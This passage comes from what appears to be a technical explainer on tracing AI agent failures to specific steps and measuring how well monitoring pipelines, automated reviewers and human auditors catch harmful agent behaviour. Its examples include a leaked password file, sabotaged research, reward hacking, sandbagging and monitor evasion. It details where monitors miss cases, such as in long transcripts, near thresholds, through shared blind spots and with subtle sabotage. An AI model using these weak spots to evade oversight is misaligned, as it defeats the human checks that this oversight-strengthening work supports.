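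Restoring an environment exactly can require more than its saved files. *Attributing Agent Failures to Their History Needs an Executed Counterfactual* (Pakhomov and Nijkamp, 2026) tested saved states in an environment where tools sometimes fail at random. Although the saved files were identical, continuing from them gave different results from the original run in 9 of 24 cases when tools failed 5% of the time, and in 20 of 24 when they failed 20% of the time. The snapshots lacked the position in the sequence of random numbers that determined when tools failed. Saving that position as well removed every difference.

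Five restored copies agreed with each other in all 24 cases, so comparing copies would not have revealed the error. Pakhomov and Nijkamp recommend comparing reruns with the original run and reporting how often they agree. The test used a fixed program instead of a language model, and the final grades did not change, so the error's effect on real investigations is unknown.

The edited text also has to fit the state of the environment. If the investigator deletes the copy command from the history but leaves the copied file on the test machine, the agent continues in a situation that could never have occurred. Replacing a sentence with a harmless one of the same length is usually safer than deleting it, because it preserves the transcript's length and layout.

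### Cheaper reruns

A rerun from step 340 takes 272 steps to reach step 612. *Beyond Skill Evolution* (2026) avoids most of this computation by generating only the agent's next action, several times with the original context and several times with an edited one. In the running example, the investigator would stop at step 611 and compare how often the next command copies the password file under each context. This method again keeps the steps between 340 and 612 fixed. If the agent's software had already replaced step 340 with a summary, editing the original sentence would have no effect.

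Another option is to rerun only some steps. *Learning Which Evidence-Seeking Decisions Matter* (2026) predicts every action's effect and replays a random sample to correct the predictions. Each correction is the prediction error divided by the chance of being sampled. If the predicted effect is 0.1, the observed effect is 0.3 and the chance is 10%, the action's estimate becomes 0.1 + 0.2/0.1, or 2.1. That is far above the observed effect, but the errors average out over many actions. The method is therefore much more useful for learning which kinds of step tend to matter than for explaining a single leak.

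### How well models name the decisive step

In most benchmarks, a language model reads a failed run and names the decisive step without rerunning anything. Who&When (Zhang et al., 2025) is the usual starting point. Three experts labelled its 184 failures of multi-agent systems, and the best of three methods named the exact step in 14.2% of cases. The table shows the results with GPT-4o on the longer, hand-built part of the dataset.

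| Method | Tokens per failure | Exact step | Within five steps |
|---|---|---|---|
| Read the whole log at once | 17,106 | 4.4% | 43% |
| Judge one step after another | 87,720 | 7.9% | 34% |
| Repeatedly choose the half with the error | 34,659 | 6.9% | 36% |

All three methods had close to zero accuracy on logs of 93 to 130 steps. Reading the whole log was the worst method for finding the exact step but the best for finding its approximate location, which may be enough if a person then reads the nearby steps.

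Newer models do better, but they are still less accurate on long runs. In August 2026, Qi and colleagues tested seven models, including Gemini 3.1 Pro and Claude Opus 4.6, and three earlier diagnostic systems. The accuracy of these baselines fell from 35–50% on short runs to below 15% on long ones. The accuracy of their own method, TRAJDEBUG, stayed above 20% on the longest runs.

TRAJDEBUG first checks each step for errors, reading the current step in full and distant ones in summary. To report an error, it has to quote both the mistaken statement and the instruction or earlier result that it contradicts. It then checks whether the agent later repaired each error, and chooses the cause from the errors that still affected the outcome. The summaries mattered most, as cutting off long histories instead lowered average accuracy on the paper's two new test sets from 39% to 18%.

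TRAJDEBUG's more accurate diagnoses helped agents retry failed tasks only slightly better than feedback from simply asking the same model to find the error. The average success rate rose by 10.8 percentage points with TRAJDEBUG's feedback and by 9.2 points with the simpler method.

### Labels that no rerun has confirmed

People labeled these datasets by reading the runs, and their labels may not identify the true cause. In Who&When, the experts were unsure about 15% to 30% of their labels. *Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* found that a rule that always picks the last step is right 67% to 96% of the time on the datasets it examined. The same rule did little better than chance on failures where a replay could confirm the decisive step. Only 66 of the 596 failures in the paper's own collection had a step that could be confirmed this way. In most of the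 others, the agent had given up.

A leak, unlike giving up, must have at least one action as its cause, but a benchmark for harmful runs should still confirm its labels by intervention. According to *ReCast* (2026), Who&When Pro does this for failed tasks. Its developers inserted one error into each of many successful runs and kept the runs that then failed, which gave 12,326 runs with a known cause. However, the errors are artificial and may be easier or harder to find than natural ones.

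The choice between labels and reruns also changes which models look best. In the Canale and Soulis study, GPT-6 Astra agreed most often with the step other models chose, but it ranked eighth of 13 when scored on whether its replacements worked in reruns.

### Dilution when tracing training data

Averaging over tokens also causes problems when researchers trace what a model has learned back to documents in its training data. In *Elucidating the Design Space of LM Data Attribution* (October 2026), Yu, Wang and colleagues trained a small model on invented facts, so they knew which documents had taught it each fact. They used gradients to estimate how much each document contributed to an answer.

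In one test, each of 50 facts appeared in 50 documents, and other documents imitated the wording of the questions. The table shows the share of the right documents that ranked in the top 50.

| Tokens included in a document's score | Standard loss | Log-odds loss |
|---|---|---|
| All, averaged | 1% | 35% |
| Ten highest-scoring | 30% | 100% |

Averaging hid the few tokens that stated the fact, much as it hides the 200 tokens of step 612. The standard loss made this worse because its gradient for a token contains the factor 1 − *p*, where *p* is the probability the model gives that token. Once the model has learned a fact well and *p* is 0.99, the gradient is a hundredth of what the log-odds loss would give.

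Repetition also made attribution harder. One established method found about 90% of the right documents when each fact appeared once, but less than 10% when it appeared in 50 documents.

These results don't carry over directly to transcripts, because a training document affects the model's weights, while a step in a transcript affects only the text the model reads. Researchers can verify a step's influence on a verdict by running the monitor on an edited transcript, but to verify a document's influence they have to retrain the model without it. Taking the top ten tokens also made little difference on an existing benchmark. It changed the result by at most six percentage points, and most of the gain came from the log-odds loss.

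A plain keyword search did well on the invented facts because the questions and the right documents shared rare names. An investigator can try a keyword search first too. In the running example, searching for earlier mentions of "settings file" would find step 340 within seconds.

### Finding one step in ten tests

If exactly one step determines the monitor's verdict, an investigator can find it by repeatedly halving the transcript. The first test gives the monitor steps 1 to 500. If the monitor doesn't flag them, the decisive step is among steps 501 to 1,000, and the next test covers steps 501 to 750. Ten tests are enough for 1,000 steps because 2¹⁰ is 1,024. In the running example, the range shrinks to 501–750, 501–625, 564–625 and so on until only step 612 remains. Because the tests get shorter, the monitor processes only about 500,000 tokens across all ten.

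An investigator can use the same search to look for the reason behind the agent's command. The investigator hides half of the 611 earlier steps, has the agent generate its next action and checks whether it still copies the file. The search works only if a single step is responsible and every test gives the right answer.

The search can stop at the first split when either of two steps is enough to cause the outcome. Suppose the agent had also read the same instruction in another file at step 150. Hiding steps 1 to 305 leaves the instruction at step 340, and hiding steps 306 to 611 leaves the one at step 150. The agent copies the file both times, so neither half seems to matter.

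Interactions between steps cause a different error. If the agent copied the file only because it had read the guide and then seen the tests fail at step 611, hiding either step prevents the leak. The search will find one of the two and miss the other. Similarly, the monitor may flag three payments of $3,100 only when they appear together, so a search that separates them finds nothing in either half. Testing every pair among 1,000 steps would take 499,500 tests, and finding the three payments would require testing triples.

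Errors in individual tests also add up. If each of ten tests is right 90% of the time, all ten are right only 35% of the time. The halving method in the Who&When table had a model choose which half of the log contained the error, without rerunning anything. The logs averaged about 52 steps, or roughly six halvings, so an accuracy of 6.9% corresponds to choosing the correct half about 64% of the time, compared with 50% for a coin toss.

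### How many reruns a comparison takes

Reruns of the same agent vary, so comparing one rerun with a step and one without it shows very little about the step's effect. *Counterfactual Rollout Replay* (2026), which uses such pairs to train coding agents, warns that a single pair does not establish what an action caused. Even five reruns of each version leave a lot of doubt. In the refund example, if the change had no effect and three of the ten reruns succeeded, the split of zero successes against three would still occur about 8% of the time.

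The table gives the number of reruns needed for an 80% chance of detecting a difference, using a two-sided test at the 5% level.

| Comparison | Leak rates | Reruns of each version |
|---|---|---|
| Original and edited run, smaller leak rates | 30% and 10% | 62 |
| Original and edited run, effect of 30 points | 50% and 20% | 39 |
| Original and edited run, effect of 10 points | 50% and 40% | 388 |
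| Two edits, with effects of 30 and 10 points | 20% and 40% | 82 |

If the guide at step 340 raises the chance of a leak from 10% to 30%, confirming this takes 62 reruns with the original sentence and 62 with a harmless one. Each rerun takes 272 steps, so the total is about 34,000 steps, or 34 times the length of the transcript. Detecting an effect of 10 percentage points takes about ten times as many reruns as detecting one of 30 points.

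For a search by halving to have a 95% chance of getting all ten tests right, each test has to be right 99.5% of the time. Telling a leak rate of 30% from one of 10% with that certainty takes about 206 reruns of each version. The ten tests then take about 2,060 reruns of edited versions, plus 206 of the original, which all the tests can share if they start from the same step. Generating 2,266 single actions at step 612 may be practical, but 2,266 reruns from the beginning would not be for most investigations.

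### Why some step always ranks first

Ranking steps by their apparent effect on the outcome always puts some step at the top, even when none of them matters. Suppose the leak rate is 30% whatever the investigator changes. The investigator replaces each of the 1,000 steps in turn, rerunning the agent five times for each replacement. The chance of no leak in five reruns is 0.7⁵, or 17%, so replacing any one of about 168 steps would seem to prevent the leak completely.

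More reruns reduce the problem but don't remove it. With 20 reruns per step, about eight steps would still show at most one leak, so their leak rate would appear to fall from 30% to 5% or less. Attention has the same weakness, because some token must receive the most attention.

Diagnoses by language models vary too. When Canale and Soulis asked the same model twice about each of 62 failures, it chose the same step both times for 74% of them. The ranking of the 13 models was also uncertain: the best scored 51 points and the worst 32, but none of the 78 pairwise differences was significant after correction for multiple comparisons.

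The remedy is to test candidate steps on reruns that weren't used to choose them. An investigator might take the top five steps from an attribution method, a keyword search or a first round of reruns. Each candidate then gets two sets of fresh reruns from the same starting point, one with the step changed and one with a placebo. Testing each candidate at the 1% level keeps the chance of any false finding at or below 5%. An 80% chance of detecting a fall in the outcome's rate from 30% to 10% requires about 92 reruns per set, or 920 in total.

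The investigator should estimate the effect only from the fresh reruns, to avoid the circular analysis described in the previous section. The investigator also has to choose the replacement text before seeing the new results, because trying several wordings and keeping the one that prevents the most leaks would reintroduce the same bias.

If step 340 passes this test, the company can correct the guide and check which other agents have read it. If no candidate passes, the leak may have had several causes, or the effect of each step may be too small to detect with the available reruns. Some failures also have no simple repair. In the tests by Canale and Soulis, 5 of the 62 failed runs never succeeded with any replacement the 13 models proposed.

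## Estimating review load and missed cases in deployment

A company that runs a monitor can investigate a leak only after a flag reaches a person, so it needs to know how many transcripts its reviewers will have to read and how many harmful ones they will never see. It can count the transcripts in the review queue, but it has to estimate how many harmful ones the monitor missed.

### From a probe's flag to a human reviewer

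OpenAI's layered system, described at the start, begins with probes and ends with human responders, which keeps costs down because the cheapest check covers the most transcripts. Hall and Thompson (2026), in *How reliably can AI audit AI?*, report that METR spent roughly $400,000, or about $300 per transcript, on AI analysis when it investigated an incident that left about 1,300 transcripts and 1.2 million file fragments. At that price, the company in the running example would spend about $3 million a day to investigate all 10,000 of its transcripts, though a routine flag needs far less work.

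The table follows one day's traffic at that company through a simplified pipeline with invented error rates. Ten of the transcripts are harmful.

| Check | Harmful transcripts it passes on | Clean transcripts it passes on | Harmful left | Clean left |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Probe | 95% | 5% | 9.5 | 500 |
| Model reviewer | 90% | 10% | 8.6 | 50 |
| Investigating agent | 90% | 20% | 7.7 | 10 |
| Human reviewer | 90% | 5% | 6.9 | 0.5 |

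People read about 18 transcripts a day, and nearly half of those are harmful. But the pipeline's recall is 0.95 × 0.9 × 0.9 × 0.9, or 69%, even though each check has a recall of at least 90%. Improving the later checks can't raise the total above 95%, because the probe has already dropped 5% of the harmful transcripts.

The reviewers' workload depends on what they have to judge. If the monitor highlights step 612, a person can confirm within minutes that the agent copied the password file. If reviewers have to read whole transcripts at 90 minutes each, 18 of them take 27 hours, which is more than three people can do in a working day. The number of flags also varies from day to day. Even if flags arrived independently, about 6% of days would bring 25 or more, and real flags tend to arrive in clusters. A team with just enough reviewers for an average day will build up a backlog, and leaked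 passwords stay usable while the flagged step awaits review.

A higher threshold at the first check shortens the review queue but misses real cases. In *Models watching models*, Olickel (2026) ran Jev, the model mentioned earlier that gives probabilities, on 220,297 real tool calls. At a threshold of 0.5, it flagged 3,814 of them, or 1.73%. At that rate, a transcript of 1,000 steps would contain about 17 flags. Olickel's counts imply that a threshold of 0.6 would leave 1,055 flags and a threshold of 0.7 would leave 293. But two of the hazards Olickel reviewed, both calls that exposed credentials, scored 0.59 and 0.58, so a threshold of 0.6 would have missed them.

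### When the checks make the same mistakes

Multiplying the four recalls gives the overall recall if the team measured each one on the transcripts that reach that check. If the team instead tested each check separately on the same set of harmful transcripts, which may be easier, the product is correct only if the checks make their mistakes independently.

Suppose the recalls in the table came from such separate tests. If the checks tend to miss the same transcripts, the pipeline's recall can be as high as 90%, the recall of its weakest check. If no two checks miss the same transcript, the misses add up to 35% and recall is 65%. Multiplying the recalls gives 69%, which is near the bottom of this range, so the pipeline's recall would be higher than that estimate if the misses overlap heavily.

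Overlapping false positives greatly increase the review load. If the first three checks wrongly flag 5%, 10% and 20% of all clean transcripts independently, 0.1% of clean transcripts will be flagged by all three and reach a person, or about 10 a day. But if the probe flags a session of legitimate security work, the model reviewer probably will too. With complete overlap, all 500 clean transcripts that the probe flags each day would reach a person.

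Overlapping misses also do more harm when a team adds a second monitor as a backup and reviews anything either one flags. Two monitors that each miss 10% of harmful transcripts will together miss 1% if their misses are independent, but 10% if they miss the same transcripts.

According to Hall and Thompson, METR's investigation found that GPT-5.6 Sol often uncritically adopted the viewpoint of the agent whose transcript it was reading, which can cause such overlap. If the agent in the running example wrote that it was following the guide's instructions when it copied the settings file, a reviewer and an investigating agent built on the same model might both accept that explanation. A team can measure this overlap by sending the same harmful transcripts through the whole pipeline and recording where each one stops.

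### How reliable the human check is

OpenAI's *Misalignment monitoring*, a guide for developers, describes a flag as a sign that an agent's actions need review. A flag doesn't prove that the agent disobeyed its instructions, so a reviewer has to decide whether it did. Companies usually treat that decision as the correct answer when they evaluate their monitors.

Shenoy, Zang and colleagues (2026), in *Auditors Struggle to Catch Sabotage In End-to-End Transcripts of AI Safety Research*, tested how often people decide correctly in a difficult setting. A researcher ran ten new AI safety experiments honestly, then produced 12 sabotaged versions meant to reach a wrong main conclusion. Twenty-five auditors did 104 audits of the experiment records, which included the code, the final report and a log of file changes and terminal commands. For each record, they had 90 minutes of working time, could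 use AI assistants and rerun experiments, and received two audits written by Claude Opus 4.8.

The auditors gave each record a probability of sabotage. Their AUROC (the chance that a sabotaged record gets a higher probability than an honest one) was 0.59, compared with 0.5 for guessing. The 95% confidence interval runs from 0.37 to 0.77, so the result is compatible with either no ability or a moderate ability to detect sabotage. The AUROC was 0.51 after 30 minutes and 0.56 after 60, but the improvement could be due to chance.

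With a threshold of 54%, the auditors flagged 51% of the sabotaged records and 31% of the honest ones. Lowering it to 30% raised recall to 82% and the false positive rate to 73%. Shenoy and colleagues also calculate that if only 1% of projects were sabotaged, about 1.6% of the audits flagged at a 50% threshold would involve sabotage, so a flag would barely raise the probability that a project was sabotaged.

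If the human reviewers in the table performed like these auditors at the 54% threshold, they would escalate about four of the day's ten harmful transcripts and three clean ones. They would probably do much better with step 612, because a copied password file is easier to recognise than a deliberately poor experimental design. Other people's sabotage could be easier or harder to detect, since all the sabotage here came from one researcher.

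Auditors in the study also tended to miss the same flaws. The sabotaged records contained 33 separate flaws, and auditors had 155 opportunities to find one. They identified the flaw at least partly in 41 cases, or 26%. With an average of 4.7 audits per flaw, about eight flaws would have escaped every auditor if misses were independent, but 16 did. The Opus 4.8 audits fully identified one of these 16, but none of the people who received those audits reported it.

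In one record, all five auditors at least partly identified one major flaw, but none found the other two. So a reviewer who has confirmed one harmful step should still check the rest of the flagged material.

Newer AI models were probably better than people at naming the flaws. With half credit for partial answers, Claude Fable 5.1 averaged 37% and GPT-6 Astra 33%, compared with 22% for the human auditors. The models' AUROCs were 0.73 and 0.74, although they could not run experiments. The differences from the human results were not statistically significant. Thirteen of the 33 flaws were not fully identified in any human or AI report.

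Hall and Thompson found much better results for misbehaviour that shows more clearly in a transcript. They tested several models on MALT, METR's labelled collection. At a false positive rate of 5%, the strongest models caught nearly all the reward hacking and about 80% of the sandbagging. That rate would still produce about 500 false alarms a day at the company. Hall and Thompson consider such auditors extremely useful for estimating how common misbehaviour is, but not good enough when a company has to catch nearly every case. Two other models, Fable 5 and Opus 5, refused to label the logs, so a pipeline also needs a rule for transcripts that a model refuses to judge.

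### From the share flagged to the share harmful

The share of transcripts that a monitor flags differs from the share that are harmful, because it includes false alarms and leaves out misses. If the monitor flags a share *q*, has recall *R* and a false positive rate *F*, the base rate is

π = (*q* − *F*) / (*R* − *F*).

Zhang's study of coding sessions, described at the start, shows how much this correction matters. Its judges flagged severe monitor evasion in 1.9% of the public sessions and severe overselling in 1.8%. Overselling means making false, misleading or overconfident claims about one's own work. In one session, the agent deleted an integration test that it had failed to convert, then announced that it had converted the integration tests.

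A case counted as severe if it involved blatant and persistent behaviour, evidence of malicious intent, or serious consequences, such as when an agent pushed unreviewed code directly to production. To build each judge, the Transluce team had Claude Fable expand a short description into a detailed rubric, which people then reviewed and rewrote where necessary. The rubric's worked examples came from sessions the team had spot-checked. Two later steps targeted false positives among severe cases.

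Checking flagged cases can lower *F*, but it doesn't find cases the judge never flagged. The table shows what a flag rate of 1.9% would imply under different assumptions about the judge.

| Judge's recall | No false positives | False positive rate 0.5% | False positive rate 1% |
|---|---|---|---|
| 90% | 2.1% | 1.6% | 1.0% |
| 50% | 3.8% | 2.8% | 1.8% |

Transluce's own sessions had almost no flags, which is evidence against a false positive rate as high as 1%. Recall is harder to determine, and the estimate changes by a factor of almost two between the two recall values in the table. Zhang also warns against comparing the rates of different agent models, because each model worked on a different, non-random set of sessions.

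### Planting known cases

A team can measure recall directly by planting harmful steps in copies of real transcripts and sending the copies through the live pipeline without telling the reviewers. Planting five transcripts a day would add about four human reviews a day and provide 100 test cases in 20 days. If reviewers escalate 70 of the 100, the pipeline's recall on these cases is 70%, with a 95% confidence interval of about 60% to 79%. The team can use records of where the other 30 stopped to find the check that most needs improvement.

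The result applies to real harm only if the planted cases are about as hard to detect as real ones. Recorded incidents are realistic, but a company has records only of incidents that somebody noticed. Invented cases can cover harm that nobody has noticed yet, but they may be too obvious. OpenAI tests its monitoring on recorded incidents and simulated attacks. It also audits current internal traffic and uses red-teaming, in which testers deliberately look for weaknesses. OpenAI's *How we measure alignment* (2026) also discusses whether results from the company's standard tests of model behaviour hold in real use.

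The sabotage study shows that the choice of cases can strongly affect the result. Before seeing any audits, the researcher rated how easy each sabotaged record would be to audit. Across all the rated records, human auditors scored about 25% at identifying flaws, with major flaws counting for more. On the three records rated hardest, neither people nor AI models identified any flaws, although people were no less suspicious of those records overall. A team should therefore report recall separately for easy and hard planted cases, because an average mostly reflects how many of each the team planted.

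### What companies' published tests leave out

*Evaluating Offline Monitoring of Internal AI Agents*, from the AI policy research organisation GovAI, makes a similar criticism of the only two companies its authors know to have published information about such monitoring. "Offline" means that the monitor reads actions after the agent has taken them.

Anthropic reports how often its monitors flag planted attacks, but not how many of those attacks reach a human reviewer after later filters discard some flags. In the pipeline above, a company could truthfully report that its probe flags 95% of harmful transcripts, even though only 77% reach a person and 69% lead to an escalation.

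OpenAI reports that its monitor flags every transcript that employees had independently flagged. GovAI objects that this is weak evidence if employees notice only obvious misbehaviour. Suppose the monitor catches all 50 obvious incidents but only 30 of 150 subtle ones. If employees report ten incidents, all of them obvious, the monitor will have flagged all ten, even though its recall across all incidents is 80 out of 200, or 40%.

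GovAI recommends that companies use realistic planted attacks and publish four figures:

- the share of model outputs that they monitor, for each type of deployment
- the share of planted attacks that reach human review
- the share of those that reviewers escalate
- the time between an attack and its detection

The share of outputs monitored multiplies recall, just as another check at the start of the pipeline would. If the company monitors only 80% of its agents' runs and harm is equally common in the rest, its overall recall falls from 69% to 55%. In October 2026, OpenAI listed tests that go beyond a comparison with employee reports, but listing them doesn't answer GovAI's question about how many planted attacks reach a person.

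### No errors in 300 transcripts

A monitor can make no errors in a small test and still raise many false alarms in deployment. If it flags none of 300 clean transcripts, its false positive rate may still be 1% by the 3/*n* limit from earlier sections (the "rule of three"), which would mean 100 false alarms a day at the company.

The same rule applies to misses. A pipeline that catches all 30 planted cases may still miss up to about 10% of cases like them. If the 30 cases are small variations on three ideas, they provide much less evidence than 30 different ones.

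### Reading transcripts that nobody flagged

Planted cases cover only the kinds of harm that the team thought of. To find other kinds, reviewers can read a random sample of the transcripts that the monitor did not flag, but very few of these are harmful. The pipeline in the table misses about three harmful transcripts a day among the nearly 10,000 that it doesn't escalate, so a random sample of 300 would have less than a 10% chance of including any of them.

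A better sample includes a larger share of the transcripts that scored just below the threshold. Each harmful transcript in the sample must then also represent similar ones that nobody read, so if reviewers read one in five, each harmful one counts as five. The table shows a hypothetical month in which the monitor left 300,000 transcripts unflagged.

| Monitor's score | Unflagged transcripts | Reviewed | Harmful ones found | Weight of each | Estimated misses |
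|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Just below the threshold | 3,000 | 600 | 6 | 5 | 30 |
| Medium | 27,000 | 540 | 1 | 50 | 50 |
| Low | 270,000 | 540 | 0 | 500 | 0 |

The estimate is 80 missed transcripts. If the company confirmed 240 harmful transcripts among those the monitor flagged, the monitor's recall would be 240 out of 320, or 75%. But by the rule of three, finding no harmful transcripts in 540 low-scoring ones still allows a rate as high as 0.56%, or 1,500 more misses among the 270,000, which would reduce recall to 13%. Lowering that limit to 30 misses would require reviewing about 27,000 low-scoring transcripts.

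The weights also magnify reviewers' mistakes. Wrongly marking one low-scoring transcript as harmful adds 500 to the estimate, so a second person should confirm every transcript marked as harmful. Harmful transcripts that reviewers overlook lower the estimate. If reviewers recognised only half of the harmful transcripts in the sample, the true number of missed cases would be about 160, not the estimated 80.

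A stronger model can read a much larger sample than people can, and people can then check what it flags. This works best if the model differs from the ones in the pipeline, because a model that overlooks the same transcripts as the original monitor will find few misses and make the monitor's recall look better than it is.

### Separate results for long transcripts

Overall recall can also hide the effect of transcript length. In the next table, a team has planted 200 harmful steps, mostly in short transcripts because those are the most common. To estimate the total number of real cases in each length group, the team divides the number the pipeline caught by the recall for that group.

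| Transcript length | Planted cases caught | Recall | Real cases caught | Estimated real cases | Estimated misses |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Up to 100 steps | 152 of 160 | 95% | 19 | 20 | 1 |
| 101 to 500 steps | 24 of 30 | 80% | 24 | 30 | 6 |
| Over 500 steps | 4 of 10 | 40% | 20 | 50 | 30 |
| All | 180 of 200 | 90% | 63 | 100 | 37 |

Using the overall recall of 90%, the team would estimate that it had missed about seven real cases. The estimate rises to 37 with the separate figures, and 30 of those cases are in transcripts of more than 500 steps, like the running example. Long transcripts give an agent more opportunities to do harm, so they can contain half of the real cases even if they are a small share of the traffic.

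The figure for long transcripts is based on only ten planted cases. With four of ten caught, recall could be from 12% to 74%, so the number of real cases in long transcripts could be from 27 to 164. If the team moved 90 of its planted cases from short transcripts to long ones and again caught 40%, the range for real cases would narrow to 40 to 66.
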